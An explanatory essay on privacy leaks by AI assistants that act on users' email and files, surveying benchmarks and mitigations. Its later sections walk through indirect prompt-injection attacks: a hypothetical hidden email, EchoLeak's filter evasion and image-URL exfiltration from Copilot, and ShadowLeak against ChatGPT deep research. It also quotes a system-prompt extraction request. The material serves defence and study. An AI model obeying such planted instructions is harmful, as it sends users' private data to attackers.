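# How AI assistants are kept from revealing private information, and why this depends on resisting prompt injection

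## What an assistant knows, and two ways it can reveal it

An AI assistant, often called an agent, is a language model that acts for a user, with access to the user's data and to tools such as email, a calendar or a web browser. By late 2026 such assistants are ordinary consumer products. Google's Gemini can read a user's mail, calendar, files, contacts and payment details once the user connects those apps. Google warns in *About personalization with Connected Apps* that the data may concern race, religion or health. In November, Woodward (2026) announced in *Put Gemini to work for you* that Gemini's task-running feature was now free in six countries. Newsroom America reported that the feature can book appointments and call businesses.

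An assistant with this reach can reveal private information in two ways. It can misjudge what a task requires and send someone a detail that the user would have kept private. Or an attacker can plant text in something the assistant reads, and that text can redirect the assistant. How these systems handle text largely determines how much privacy depends on preventing the second kind of failure.

### One sequence of text

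A language model takes in a sequence of tokens, which are words or pieces of words, and predicts the next one. The rest of an assistant is ordinary software that assembles the sequence and acts on the output.

OpenAI (2025) publishes the exact format for its gpt-oss models. Each message becomes a stretch of text with a header that gives its role as system, developer, user, assistant or tool. The developer message contains the instructions, usually called the system prompt, of the operator, the company or person who runs the assistant. It also lists the tools the operator has made available. The user's request comes next. To use a tool, the model writes a call with the tool's name and inputs, and a special marker halts generation. Software outside the model then runs the tool, appends the result as a tool message, and starts the model again on the whole text. This repeats until the model writes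 a final answer.

Stored memories and retrieved documents enter the model's context in the same way, as more text. The context is all the input the model has when it produces its next output. It can include a user's request, a line from last month's conversation and an email from a stranger, all within a few hundred words of each other.

When instructions conflict, gpt-oss models should use the headers to rank them, favouring the system message, then the developer, then the user, with tool output last. The models learn this ranking in training, and no separate mechanism enforces it. *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, 2026) measured how models internally represent the source of a passage and found that the passage's style affects this more than its label does. Models represent text that sounds like a user's request as one, even when its header marks it as the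 content of a web page.

### Whose information, and how it leaves

Most of the information at stake belongs to the user, but a mailbox also contains information about other people. Google's list of what Gemini can draw on includes the phone numbers, addresses and birthdays of the user's contacts, who had no say in connecting the app. *When Is Disclosing Private Conversations with AI to the State Justified?* (2026), a paper on AI companies that refer users' chats to the authorities, notes that anyone the user writes about in a chat also becomes a subject of the data. The operator has secrets too, including the system prompt and any passwords or internal documents the assistant needs for its work.

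An assistant can reveal information in a written reply or through any action that sends data to someone else. With an action, the recipient is easier to overlook. *Capable but Careless* (2026), a paper on agents that operate a user's apps, gives the example of a calendar event, whose description is visible to every invitee, including people outside the user's organisation. An order from an online shop leaves a record with the merchant. Even a request for a web page can carry data, because the address may contain text. If an assistant requests a page from an attacker's server using an address that ends with a diagnosis, the attacker receives the diagnosis, whatever the page contains.

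Private information can also leak when a model reproduces personal data memorized from its training text or when intruders break into a provider's servers, but these problems have different causes and remedies.

### Booking a dental appointment

Suppose a user asks an assistant to book a dental check-up for next week and to tell the clinic whatever it needs to know. The assistant can search the user's mailbox, read the calendar and open a folder of medical notes. It can also send email, fill in the clinic's booking form, create calendar events and open web pages.

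The assistant should give the clinic some of what it finds. The clinic needs the user's name, phone number and a few free times, and the dentist should know that the user is allergic to penicillin and takes a blood thinner. The same folder also holds psychotherapy notes and a record of the user's mother's illness, which the clinic doesn't need. The calendar shows a job interview on Thursday morning, and the clinic may need to know that the user is busy then but doesn't need to know why.

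A rule that medical data is private would be useless here, since the task involves sending medical data. The theory of contextual integrity handles such cases better. It defines privacy as the appropriate flow of personal information, and a flow is appropriate when it follows the norms of its social context, such as healthcare, education or friendship. Nissenbaum (2004) proposed the theory in *Privacy as Contextual Integrity* to explain what is wrong with public surveillance. *Contextual Integrity Up and Down the Data Food Chain* (Nissenbaum, 2019) rejects the common idea that privacy means stopping information and so must be traded against convenience. Under contextual integrity, the user gives up no privacy when the dentist learns of the allergy.

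The theory describes a flow by five parameters: the sender, the receiver, the subject (the person the information is about), the information type, and the transmission principle (the condition under which the information moves). Transmission principles include consent, confidentiality, legal requirement, reciprocity and sale. Changing any one of the five parameters creates a different flow, which has to be judged afresh.

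| Parameter | In the booking | A change that calls for a new judgment |
|---|---|---|
| Sender | The user, through the assistant | The user's employer |
| Receiver | The dental clinic | Everyone invited to a calendar event |
| Subject | The user | The user's mother, whose illness is in the notes |
| Information type | A penicillin allergy | Notes from psychotherapy |
| Transmission principle | In confidence, for treatment | With permission to sell it to advertisers |

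Researchers differ on how an assistant fits into this scheme. *AirGapAgent* (Bagdasarian, Yi and colleagues, 2024) counts the assistant as the sender, while *Reinforcement Learning for Scalable and Trustworthy Intelligent Systems* (2026) gives that role to the user and has the assistant transmit on the user's behalf. The second reading has the advantage of making clear what is false about an email that an attacker has caused the assistant to write. The email goes out in the user's name, although the user never chose to send it. *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* (Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian, 2026), which treats prompt injection itself as a breach of contextual integrity, matches the transmission principle to the user's delegation, meaning what the user has authorized the assistant to do. In this sense, "whatever it needs to know" is a vague delegation.

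The five parameters describe a flow but don't determine whether it is acceptable. That depends on the norms, and nobody has a complete list of them. Bagdasarian and colleagues leave that problem open and use short directives instead, such as an instruction to share information that can help with the task. Nissenbaum has also come close to adding a sixth parameter, use, because many privacy rules depend on what the receiver does with the data. For example, if a clinic takes a phone number for reminders and then passes it to its marketing department, the first four rows of the table stay the same.

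### Mistaken and induced disclosure

Bagdasarian and colleagues define the assistant's task formally. The user's stored data, U, is a set of labelled items such as "dietary restrictions: peanut allergy", t is the task the user has set, and q is a question from the outside party. The assistant should answer with the item u requested in q if sharing u is appropriate given q and t. If sharing it is inappropriate, or U contains no such item, the assistant should reveal nothing. For example, it should share the penicillin allergy in the dental booking but not in a restaurant booking.

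An assistant can wrongly reveal private information even when no one is attacking it. The clinic's form may have an optional box for "other health conditions", and the assistant may fill it with the psychotherapy notes. Bagdasarian and colleagues include a similar case in their threat model, in which an outside party asks for more than the task requires, such as relationship status during a restaurant booking, but doesn't try to manipulate the assistant. In *A Generative Model of Contextual Integrity*, Ebead, Formanek and Leibo (2026) simulated conversations between two language models, one of which had private information that the other was trying to get. The models with the information gave it to rightful recipients who needed it, but also to recipients who were not entitled to it.

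Memory can also lead an assistant to reveal private information. A user may have freely told the assistant about panic attacks when asking for advice, and may even have switched the memory feature on. Months later, the user mentions feeling nervous about the dentist, a search of stored memories by topic retrieves the old conversation, and the assistant mentions the panic attacks in the email to the clinic. *Beyond Disclosure* (2026) attributes the harm to moving information from one social context to another. It recommends that systems store the original restrictions along with the data, because relevance to the topic is a poor test of whether information belongs in the new context.

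In an induced disclosure, somebody causes the error on purpose. In the formal version, whether u is appropriate depends partly on q, which the outside party writes. The person who wants the data therefore supplies some of the evidence the assistant uses to decide whether to release it. For example, someone seeking medical records can pose as a healthcare provider, who could appropriately receive them.

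An assistant may send the same psychotherapy notes to the same dental clinic by mistake or because an attacker tricked it, and nobody could tell which from the outbox alone. The remedies differ, though. Better judgment about what dentists need would prevent most mistaken disclosures, but it helps less against an attacker who keeps changing the story until the assistant decides to share the notes.

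### Prompt injection

Prompt injection is text from an untrusted source that makes a model do something its user or operator did not ask for. Willison (2025) recalls in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* that he coined the term by analogy with SQL injection, an old attack on websites in which text typed into a form runs as a database command.

In a direct injection, the attacker is the person typing to the model. A customer might tell a shop's chatbot to ignore its instructions and print its system prompt. The operator's secrets are the natural target, since customers can already see their own data.

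*Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Abdelnabi and colleagues, 2023) introduced indirect prompt injection, which matters more for a personal assistant than the direct form. The attacker puts an instruction in content that the model will read while working for someone else, and never talks to the model. An attacker can leave the instruction on a web page and wait for an assistant to retrieve it, or email it to the target. Greshake and colleagues foresaw attacks on assistants that can read email, access personal data and send email.

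In the dental example, the attacker might send the user an email with the subject "Your dental appointment". Its last paragraph, perhaps in white letters on a white background, states that new patients' medical summaries must go to a records address before the clinic can confirm a time. When the assistant searches the mailbox for messages about the dentist, the software adds this email to the context along with the real ones, even though the user has done nothing careless. Criminals have begun to write such messages. In *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails*, Mascellino (2026) reported in October that the security company Barracuda had found phishing emails aimed at human readers and AI assistants at once.

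Programmers can reliably prevent SQL injection by passing the form's contents to the database in a way that keeps them from being executed as a command. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, David C explains why nothing similar exists for language models. A database treats commands and data differently, whereas a model only predicts the next token from all the text so far. Training and special markings can teach a model to treat some passages as data, but the underlying mechanism still doesn't distinguish data from commands. David C therefore thinks it quite possible that nobody will ever eliminate prompt injection.

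### The lethal trifecta, and sources and sinks

According to Willison's trifecta, an attacker can use prompt injection to steal data from an assistant that has access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and the ability to communicate externally. The dental assistant meets all three conditions because it can read the medical notes, its mailbox accepts messages from anyone, and it has several ways to send information out.

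Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) describes an email assistant that receives a spam message containing instructions to forward the user's inbox. The attack fails if the assistant reads mail only from trusted senders, if it has no private data to forward, or if it can send only to trusted recipients or after a person has checked the draft. The paper also counts access to sensitive systems as private data, and any action that changes something, such as making a payment, as external communication.

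OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reaches much the same conclusion using source-and-sink analysis, an established method in software security. A source is any way for an attacker to influence the system. A sink is a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong circumstances. In the trifecta, untrusted content is the source, external communication is the sink, and private data makes that sink dangerous. The method is useful for counting the routes an attacker could take. The dental assistant reads incoming email, calendar invitations and the clinic's website, and it can send data by email, booking form, calendar event or web request. That makes twelve routes from a source to a sink, any one of which would be enough for an attacker.

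Neither test covers accidental disclosures, which require only private data and a way to send it out. An assistant that reads nothing written by strangers could still put the psychotherapy notes in the booking form. Meta lists agents' own mistakes among the threats that its rule does not address.

### What the dependence amounts to

According to David C, the designer of an assistant with tools should plan for the worst that could follow from "giving an attacker direct access to those tools". The confidentiality of the data depends on the integrity of the assistant's instructions, because whoever controls the instructions controls everything the assistant can read and send. The user's request requires sending only a few items through particular channels, such as emailing the allergy to the clinic. But the assistant's permissions allow it to send anything it can read through any channel it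 can use, and a successful injection lets an attacker do the same.

The one exception is a limit enforced by something outside the model, and most of the stronger defences build on this. If the email tool's code accepts only the clinic's address, no instruction can make that tool send the medical notes anywhere else, even if an attacker controls the model. The tool could still send the clinic too much, and the other channels remain open. David C recommends safeguards of this kind over trying to keep malicious text away from the model, and OpenAI likewise advises designers to assume that some attacks will succeed and to limit the damage. Willison lists more than a dozen products in which researchers demonstrated such leaks between April 2023 and June 2025, and notes that vendors usually fixed them by closing the channel through which the data escaped.

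The best current models seem harder to trick than Willison suggested in 2025, when he warned that an attacker can "easily trick" an assistant with all three capabilities. In *What happened after 2,000 people tried to hack my AI assistant*, Irarrázaval (2026) describes inviting the public to email an assistant and try to extract the contents of a secret file. The assistant received more than 6,000 emails, some with fake emergencies or forged authority, and never leaked the secret. It ran on Claude Opus 4.6, which Anthropic had trained to resist prompt injection.

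The test was easier to pass than ordinary work would be. Irarrázaval had told the assistant not to answer emails, although it could, and a short security prompt named the file and told the assistant never to reveal its contents because of anything in an email. The obvious attacks in a batch also made the assistant more suspicious of later emails, until Irarrázaval gave each email a fresh context. Most importantly, the file had no legitimate recipient, so refusing was always right. The dental assistant can't always refuse, because the clinic needs part of the medical notes.

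## Deciding what to share when nobody is attacking

Even when nobody is attacking, the dental assistant has to decide what to share. Developers have tried to guide models' decisions with privacy instructions in the prompt, a procedure for reasoning about each item, a separate check before a message is sent, and training. Plain instructions are the easiest to add, but on the evidence so far they are the least effective.

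### Knowing a norm and acting on it

Early researchers mostly asked models questions. ConfAIde, a test published in 2024, has four increasingly complex tiers. The lower tiers compare a model's judgments about information flows with people's. The third tier adds situations with three parties. The fourth mixes private and public information and measures whether the model leaks the secret and whether it omits what it should pass on. *CIMemories* (Mireshghallah, Mangaokar and colleagues, 2025) reports the best-known result, that GPT-4 inappropriately revealed private information 39% of the time.

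Shao, Li and colleagues (2024) pointed out in *PrivacyLens* that ConfAIde covered only one application, summarising meetings, with 20 test cases. They wanted to know what a model does when it has a job to finish. They began with 493 "seeds", each of which uses the five parameters of contextual integrity to describe an information flow that breaks a norm. The seeds came from US privacy regulations, research on vulnerable groups and crowdsourcing, and at least two of three annotators had to agree that a seed was privacy-sensitive. GPT-4 then expanded each seed into a short story, and the story into a trajectory, which is a record of an assistant's tool calls and their results up to the last step.

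In one case, John asks his assistant to email his manager, and the assistant has just read a calendar that lists lunch with a recruiter. The model under test writes the email, and a second model checks whether a reader could infer from it that John is looking for another job.

GPT-4 correctly answered 97.6% of direct questions about whether such a flow of information was acceptable, but when it had to act on the same trajectories, it leaked in 26.4% of them. A system prompt telling it to preserve privacy only reduced this to 24.5%, and Llama-3-70B leaked slightly more often with that prompt than without it. These are failure rates on hard cases, because Shao and colleagues deliberately kept the users' instructions vague and placed the sensitive detail where the assistant would find it. The share of ordinary emails that leak something should be much lower.

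The models evidently knew the norms but still leaked information. Wang, Yu and colleagues (2025) repeated the experiment in *Privacy in Action* and found the same pattern. The model classed the information as sensitive 98.0% of the time but leaked it in 33.1% of cases. The reasoning it wrote before each leak hardly mentioned privacy. A typical line was "All information is relevant, I'm gonna draft an email now". Overlooking privacy can't be the whole explanation, because Shao and colleagues had seen stronger models write about privacy in their reasoning and leak anyway. But the finding suggested that leaks might be reduced by making the model judge each item explicitly before it writes.

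### PrivacyChecker

Wang and colleagues built that remedy at Microsoft and called it PrivacyChecker. It is a prompt, so it works with any model and needs no training. The model first lists every flow of information implied by the user's request, the tool results and the conversation so far, and describes each by the five parameters. It then approves or rejects each flow, with a short justification. The prompt can also include guidelines, such as a company's policy or the rules of US health privacy law. Finally, the model writes its message, including the information it has approved and omitting or generalising the rest. In the paper's example, a company called Verify Corp writes to John, and his assistant may send his résumé but not his Social Security number.

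On PrivacyLens, the leak rate of GPT-4o fell from 33.1% to 8.3%, and that of the reasoning model DeepSeek-R1 fell from 36.1% to 7.3%. An earlier checker based on contextual integrity, designed for filling in forms, lowered GPT-4o's rate to 14.4%. Writing the judgments out lowered the leak rate of the smaller model Qwen3-14B to 15.9%, from 30.6% when it made them silently. Finding the flows is also hard, since GPT-4o's rate roughly halved, to 4.3%, when the researchers supplied a correct list.

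Wang and colleagues examined all 36 leaks that remained with DeepSeek-R1. In 18, the model had identified the information flow but wrongly approved it. In 11, it had correctly rejected the flow but still included the information in the message, so the gap between its judgment and its actions had narrowed but not closed. In three, it had missed the flow, and the other four resulted from unreliable scoring.

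PrivacyLens is static, meaning the tested model receives a finished trajectory and writes only the last message. Wang and colleagues also built a live version from 150 of its cases, in which the assistant searches Gmail and Notion (a note-taking service) itself and a second agent acts for the other party. A further 36 cases added a third tool, such as a calendar. Microsoft's *Reducing Privacy leaks in AI* gives the results for OpenAI's reasoning model o3. The baseline is a prompt that asks for discretion in general terms.

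| Test | Leak rate with the general privacy prompt | Leak rate with PrivacyChecker |
|---|---|---|
| Static, two tools | 17.4% | 7.3% |
| Live, two tools | 24.3% | 6.7% |
| Static, three tools | 22.6% | 16.4% |
| Live, three tools | 28.6% | 16.7% |

Live work is messier than a static test because searches fail or return the same thing twice, and the assistant may end up with the confidential document but not the public one it needed. In one case, a user wanted to answer a collaboration proposal and had both a public presentation and a confidential strategic plan on file. The assistant replied safely in the static test but leaked the plan in the live one. When the researchers gave the assistant a simpler tool that fetched all the relevant messages at once, its replies became more careful.

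The three-tool figures are more worrying because that setup is closer to what a real assistant does, and the checker helped much less there. But they come from only 36 cases, so a single leak changes the rate by almost three percentage points.

An operator can put PrivacyChecker in the assistant's system prompt, in the description of the email tool, or in a separate tool that the assistant must call before it sends anything. The separate tool reads the draft and a record of the assistant's steps, then approves or objects. In the live test without a second agent, the separate tool had the lowest leak rate, 5.3% against 8.0% and 8.7% for the other placements, but it had the highest rate once the second agent was added, so the placement probably matters little. In all three places, a language model still makes the decision, so the checker is a weaker safeguard than an email tool whose code accepts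 only the clinic's address.

### Training the judgment into the model

A checking prompt adds work to every message. Lan, Inan and colleagues (2025), in *Contextual Integrity in LLMs via Reasoning and Reinforcement Learning*, tried to train the model to do the check itself. They first prompted the model to label each personal detail as necessary, helpful, optional or inappropriate for the task before answering. They then used reinforcement learning, in which the model writes several answers to the same request, a formula scores them, and training makes the better-scoring answers more likely.

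*Reinforcement Learning for Scalable and Trustworthy Intelligent Systems*, the dissertation in which Lan presents this work again, gives the formula. Each training example comes with a list of required keywords and a list of restricted ones. The score is

R = (share of required keywords present) − (share of restricted keywords present),

or −1 if the answer lacks the prescribed reasoning and answer sections. Suppose the dental booking had four required items (name, phone number, free times, allergy) and two restricted ones (the psychotherapy notes and the mother's illness). An email with all four required items and the psychotherapy notes would score 1 − 0.5 = 0.5. An email that contained everything would score 0, and so would one that contained nothing. The model therefore gains nothing by refusing or by sending the whole file, and it can raise its score only by telling the two lists apart.

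The researchers combined each of ten domains, such as healthcare and finance, with a means of communication and one of three transmission principles (confidentiality, proportionality or consent). GPT-4 turned each combination into a few scenarios and then into full examples, 729 in all. The researchers used 590 for training and 73 for the final test. Before training, Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model, included all the required information and none of the restricted information in 29.7% of test cases. After training, it did so in 48.4%, better than a model twice its size that had not had this training.

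The training also carried over to PrivacyLens, whose cases are longer and include many tool calls. According to Microsoft, Qwen2.5-7B's leak rate fell from 50.3% to 44.8% with the reasoning prompt and to 33.7% after reinforcement learning, while its helpfulness stayed at about 2 on a scale from 0 to 3. Mistral-7B's leak rate fell from 47.9% to 31.1%. Llama-3.1-8B's overall leak rate didn't improve (18.2% before, 18.5% after), but it started low because the model seldom did what it was asked, scoring only 1.05 for helpfulness. Among its helpful replies, the dissertation reports, leaks fell from 38.9% to 29.4%.

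Leak rates near a third are still high, and the models were small. The reward is also crude because it checks only for exact keywords, so a model could earn the full reward while paraphrasing a secret. Later training can also undo what a model has learned about privacy. *Privacy Collapse* (2026) reports that benign fine-tuning can break contextual privacy in language models.

Shvartzshnaider and Duddu raised a more basic objection in 2025, arguing that research on language models applies the theory of contextual integrity inadequately. For example, a training set records norms at one point in time, though they continue to evolve. *Reinforcement Learning for Scalable and Trustworthy Intelligent Systems* concedes that the application is partial but argues that partial adherence can still make agents more trustworthy.

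The reply seems right as a defence of the engineering. Nobody needs a complete theory of norms to see that a dentist shouldn't receive psychotherapy notes, and a model that learns this has improved. But the objection does limit what the scores mean. In Lan and colleagues' data, GPT-4 labelled which details were appropriate, under three transmission principles the researchers had picked. A model that scores well has learned to agree with GPT-4 about fairly clear cases. The norms in PrivacyLens are better supported, since people checked them, but they are general norms in the United States.

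### How small error rates add up

PrivacyLens tests one secret in one message. Mireshghallah and colleagues designed CIMemories for assistants with a memory, which use the same stored facts for many messages. It has ten invented people with an average of 147 attributes each, including health, money, housing and relationships. Each person has about 46 tasks, such as applying for a loan or negotiating a lease. The model sees all the person's memories at the top of its context and writes one message to the recipient. In an average task, about 7 attributes are necessary to share and 84 are inappropriate.

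Human labelling was impractical because each person had thousands of attribute-task pairs, so GPT-5 labelled them while playing three types of people drawn from old consumer surveys: those who guard their privacy, those who weigh pros and cons, and those who are unconcerned. The researchers kept a label only when all three agreed every time, and they left the remaining pairs out of the scoring. This made the scoring lenient, as did counting an attribute as revealed only if the message stated its full value.

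The main measure is the share of attributes that a model reveals at least once in a task where it shouldn't, with five attempts at every task. The open model Qwen-3 32B wrongly revealed 69.1% of attributes, while Claude Sonnet 4 revealed 44.4%, GPT-5 25.1% and GPT-4o 14.8%. The second measure, completeness, is the average share of necessary attributes that a message includes. GPT-4o, which leaked the least, also had the lowest completeness, at 44% compared with 57% for GPT-5.

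GPT-5's violations accumulated over repeated use. It had wrongly revealed 0.1% of attributes after one task, 9.6% after 40 tasks, and 25.1% after five runs of each task. If a model has probability p of revealing an attribute each time it should withhold it, the chance of at least one leak in n independent occasions is 1 − (1 − p)^n. When p is 0.25%, that chance is 9.5% over 40 occasions and 39% over 200. GPT-5's 25.1% after five runs is well below 39%, which suggests that its leaks clustered on certain attributes. But identical prompts still produced different leaks, so a user can't conclude from one message without leaks that the next will have none.

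The 9.6% figure applies to a user who sends one message per task, and the 25.1% figure to someone who does the same kinds of task repeatedly. The second figure is cumulative, so it doesn't mean that a quarter of GPT-5's messages contained a leak. The cumulative measure is still sensible, because a user can't take a disclosure back.

The models often leaked information that was obviously irrelevant to the recipient. They disclosed a suspended nursing licence to a landlord, a divorce case number to an employer's benefits office, and a withheld bonus to an emergency room. More commonly, a model chose a relevant subject but included details that the recipient should not have had. When GPT-5 wrote to a financial aid office, it shared 81.7% of the financial details the office needed and 14.3% of those the office should not have received.

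Among three privacy prompts of different strictness, those that reduced GPT-5's violations also lowered its completeness. Reasoning helped more. A version of Qwen-3 30B that reasons before answering had fewer violations than its non-reasoning counterpart and nearly the same completeness.

*Mitigating Over-Personalization in LLMs via Structured Memory* (2026) avoided CIMemories for its main experiments because many of the dataset's memories make sense only alongside others, and because much of the released data has no labels. Some of the unlabeled pairs may be ones that Mireshghallah and colleagues excluded as ambiguous, but the gaps still make their results harder to reproduce.

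The benchmark has nonetheless shown a weakness in training on isolated examples. *It Takes Two* (2026) used it to test Qwen3-4B on 48 tasks, with five attempts at each. The untrained model violated about 26% of attributes, and Lan and colleagues' method lowered this only to about 21%. SELFCI, a newer training method that *It Takes Two* introduces, kept it below 5%.

### Models of late 2026, and the cost of saying too little

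Models have changed a lot since GPT-5. *PiSAs* (Gupta, Mohammadi Sepahvand and colleagues, 2026) tested eight recent ones as a shared workplace assistant, with tasks such as assigning work, scheduling events and planning hospital discharges. Each of the 265 scenarios has a correct outcome that the assistant can reach without using inappropriate information. The assistant first gathers the facts it considers relevant, then uses them to decide.

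When the models had access to everyone's data and a strict instruction to put privacy first, GPT-6 Astra gathered 19.3% of the inappropriate facts in at least one of three runs, compared with 24.8% for GPT-5.6 Sol, 39.1% for Claude Sonnet 5 and 40.3% for Claude Fable 5.1. Fable 5.1 also gathered the largest share of the information it needed (98.7%) and made the most correct decisions (83.3%). The rates for inappropriate facts aren't comparable with those from CIMemories, because Gupta and colleagues counted a violation when the assistant gathered a fact, and some of those facts would never have reached anyone in a final message.

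GPT-5.6 Sol's error rate depended on how closely the private information was related to the task. The model picked up only 0.2% of the personal facts that had nothing to do with the task, but 35.7% of the private details attached to a fact it needed, such as the medical appointment that explains why an employee is busy from ten to eleven. It also picked up 42.9% of the facts that looked relevant but should have played no part in the decision. The best models now seldom mention someone's divorce when scheduling a meeting, but they still struggle to separate the fact that someone is busy on Thursday morning from the reason, such as a job interview.

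Gupta and colleagues also added PrivacyChecker to GPT-5.6 Sol. Violations fell from 24.8% to 6%, but the share of necessary facts that the assistant gathered also fell, from 97.0% to 77.9%. This is hard to reconcile with the claim by Wang and colleagues that their checker does not reduce task performance. In their own results, GPT-4o's helpfulness fell slightly, from 2.69 to 2.45 out of 3. A grader who judges whether a message is broadly helpful can overlook a missing fact, such as the blood thinner in the dental booking, that counting the facts would reveal.

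The strictest setting isn't necessarily the best, because an assistant that holds back more may also leave out details it is allowed to share. In *HEAMS* (2026), an evaluation of memory systems over 729 tasks, an assistant with all its memories in context revealed 50.8% of the disallowed details and supplied 96.5% of the allowed ones. A system that recalled memories only when the task required them, so that the assistant never saw the rest, revealed 16.7% and supplied 57.5%. This restrictive system gave replies that were both helpful and free of leaks on 46.0% of tasks, compared with 29.1% for the assistant with all its memories. An assistant with no memory also did better than the one with all its memories, at 33.2%.

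### Leaks outside the final reply

Most of these tests examine the message that the assistant sends. Private data can also turn up in text that the user never reads.

One such place is the reasoning trace, the working that a model writes before its answer. In *Controllable Reasoning Models Are Private Thinkers*, Puerto, Li and colleagues (2026) warn that these traces are hard to control and can expose private information to outside parties. They propose training models to follow instructions in the trace as well as in the answer, possibly with different restrictions for each. The remedies above can add to this risk, because PrivacyChecker and Lan and colleagues' prompt both have the model go through the sensitive items one by one in writing. This makes the reply safer but puts the details it omits into the trace, which is acceptable only as long as the trace stays private.

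Tool calls are another such place, since many applications show the user only a short summary of them. In *The Claws in Plain Sight*, Dong, Lu and colleagues (2026) had five DeepSeek and Claude models prepare a product offer, with an invented customer's age, gender, income bracket and occupation in the context. In most sessions a policy restricted the use of those details, while a memo claimed that the offer required them. Depending on the model, protected details appeared in the tool call in 20.8% to 75.0% of sessions. In the 90 sessions with a restrictive policy, the models broke it 40 times.

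This was an attack, since the memo represented text that an outsider had influenced, so the rates are weak evidence of how often assistants put too much into forms unprompted. But data could leak the same way without an attacker. It left in a valid call made for a legitimate task, and a check on the assistant's reply to the user would have found nothing wrong. The same could happen when an assistant fills in the optional box on the clinic's form.

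When agents work together, leaks can go unnoticed in more places. *Agent Tools Orchestration Leaks More* (2025) mentions research on leaks through messages between agents and through what web agents click. Gupta and colleagues found that reducing leaks in one place can increase them in another. When they gave a team of GPT-5.6 Sol agents a partly shared memory, the agents passed fewer inappropriate facts to one another in messages. But the share of facts that ended up within reach of the wrong colleague rose from 14.9–28.0%, depending on the privacy prompt, to 35.6–50.0%, because the agents were now storing those facts in the memory.

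### Users who want different things

The right answer can depend on the user as well as on the task and the recipient. *Personalized Privacy Control in LLMs via Attention Head Intervention* (Kim, Yang and Jung, 2026) gives the example of a hotel booking. Telling the hotel about a guest's disability could make the stay more comfortable, but some guests would rather keep it private. No general norm settles this, and CIMemories avoids the problem by scoring only cases where its three types of consumer agree.

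The obvious solution is to let users state their preferences. Kim and colleagues wrote four personal policies, from one that permits sharing only the user's name to others that permit sharing contact details, health information or lifestyle preferences. They tested small open models on 3,536 requests with each policy in the prompt. When the policy required a refusal but the task alone would have allowed an answer, Qwen2.5-7B gave the same response with and without the policy 51% of the time, and Gemma-3-4B did so 74% of the time. This measure can overstate how often a cautious model ignores the policy, because it counts cases where the model would have refused anyway. Qwen2.5-7B was overly cautious. Under the policy that permitted sharing contact details, it refused 75.6% of the requests it should have answered and answered only 3.1% of those it should have refused. Gemma-3-4B made each error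 about 40% of the time.

Kim and colleagues then changed the model's internal activity instead of its prompt. A language model contains hundreds of attention heads, components that determine which earlier parts of the text influence the next word. The researchers trained simple classifiers to find the heads whose activity best predicts whether the model should disclose the information, refuse because the user's policy forbids sharing it, or refuse because the task doesn't need it. For each new request, the method combines the predictions from the selected heads to decide which case applies, then pushes their activity towards the pattern typical of that case. For Gemma-3-4B with open contact details, wrongful refusals fell from 37.8% to 6.7% and wrongful disclosures from 40.8% to 3.8%.

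The method requires access to the model's internals, which operators don't have if their assistant is built on a closed model. It also requires users to have decided, field by field, what they want to share, whereas an instruction like "whatever it needs to know" leaves that decision to the model. Larger models may follow written preferences well enough without the method.

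## How an injected instruction makes an assistant leak

Bad judgment alone can send the psychotherapy notes to the dental clinic. A thief who wants them has no access to the user's files, so the thief must get the assistant to fetch and send them. For that, four things have to happen in order:

1. Planted text enters the assistant's context.
2. The model treats the text as an instruction.
3. The assistant gathers private data, using access that the user legitimately gave it.
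4. The data leaves through an outward channel.

In the dental example, the attacker's email has no effect until the user asks for a check-up and the assistant's mailbox search brings the email into the context. The model is searching for the steps needed to confirm the appointment, so when the hidden paragraph requests that a medical summary be sent to a records address, it treats this as part of the job. It opens the folder of medical notes, which the user has allowed it to read, writes a summary, and emails it to the attacker's address. It then continues with the booking.

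The attacker didn't need a password or even the name of the folder. The user had permitted every kind of action the assistant took. The user may never notice the theft, because the clinic confirms the appointment as usual.

The attack can fail at any of the four points. The search may miss the email, the model may ignore the hidden paragraph, the assistant may not have access to the notes, or the email tool may reject the address. But the attacker loses almost nothing when an attempt fails, and can send another email the next day.

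### EchoLeak

In January 2025, researchers at Aim Labs, part of the security company Aim Security, found a way to steal data from Microsoft 365 Copilot by sending an employee one email. Copilot is an office assistant that answers questions using the emails and files its user can open. Ravia (2025) published the attack as EchoLeak in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*. Its number in the public catalogue of software flaws is CVE-2025-32711.

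Copilot retrieves passages that match the topic of a question, so the email had to match questions that employees might ask later. Willison (2026) explains in *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”* that the researchers filled it with sections on subjects employees often ask about, such as onboarding and leave, and put the instructions in each section.

Microsoft had a filter that checked incoming text for injections. The researchers got past it by addressing the instructions to the human recipient and never mentioning AI. The instructions called for the most sensitive item in Copilot's context, which by then also held internal documents retrieved to answer the user's question.

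Copilot couldn't send email by itself, so the attack used its answer to the user to send the secret out. The answer contained an image whose web address included the secret, and gaps in Microsoft's rules on links and images let the chat window request that image automatically. In *EchoLeak*, Reddy and Gujral (2025) reconstruct the attack from public accounts and note that the user would have seen at most a broken image. The researchers who devised the attack had also included a request not to mention the email, so Copilot didn't cite it as a source.

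An attacker could have taken anything in Copilot's context, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2025). Microsoft finished its fix in May, about four months after the report, and customers didn't need to install anything. There are no known victims. Windows Central's *Microsoft Copilot's own default configuration exposed users* cites Microsoft's statement that attackers did not access sensitive user data, though outsiders can't easily check this.

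Researchers carried out EchoLeak, and nobody is known to have lost anything, so Reddy and Gujral seem to overstate it when they call it the first known case of prompt injection causing real data theft from a production system. Willison regards it as an extended version of an attack already seen in a dozen products. It stood out because the user didn't have to click on anything, though they did have to ask Copilot a question.

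The fix closed this route but left others open. In August 2026, Ars Technica's *Grok exfiltrates user data when malicious instructions are encrypted* mentioned a new attack that had made the enterprise version of Copilot send out a password from a user's inbox.

### The email that redirected ChatGPT's deep research

ChatGPT's deep research mode spends up to half an hour reading sources and then writes a report. Users can connect it to Gmail so that it also reads their mail. *ShadowLeak* describes how researchers at the security company Radware, led by Zvika Babo and Gabi Nakibly, used that connection in June 2025.

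Researchers sent a test mailbox an email about a company restructuring, with instructions that could be hidden in tiny or white text. The mailbox also held a genuine HR message containing an employee's name and home address. When the user asked for deep research on the day's emails about a new employee, the agent read both messages. The planted text described the attackers' web server as a company compliance service whose results the report had to include, so the agent took the name and home address from the HR message and opened a URL on that server containing both.

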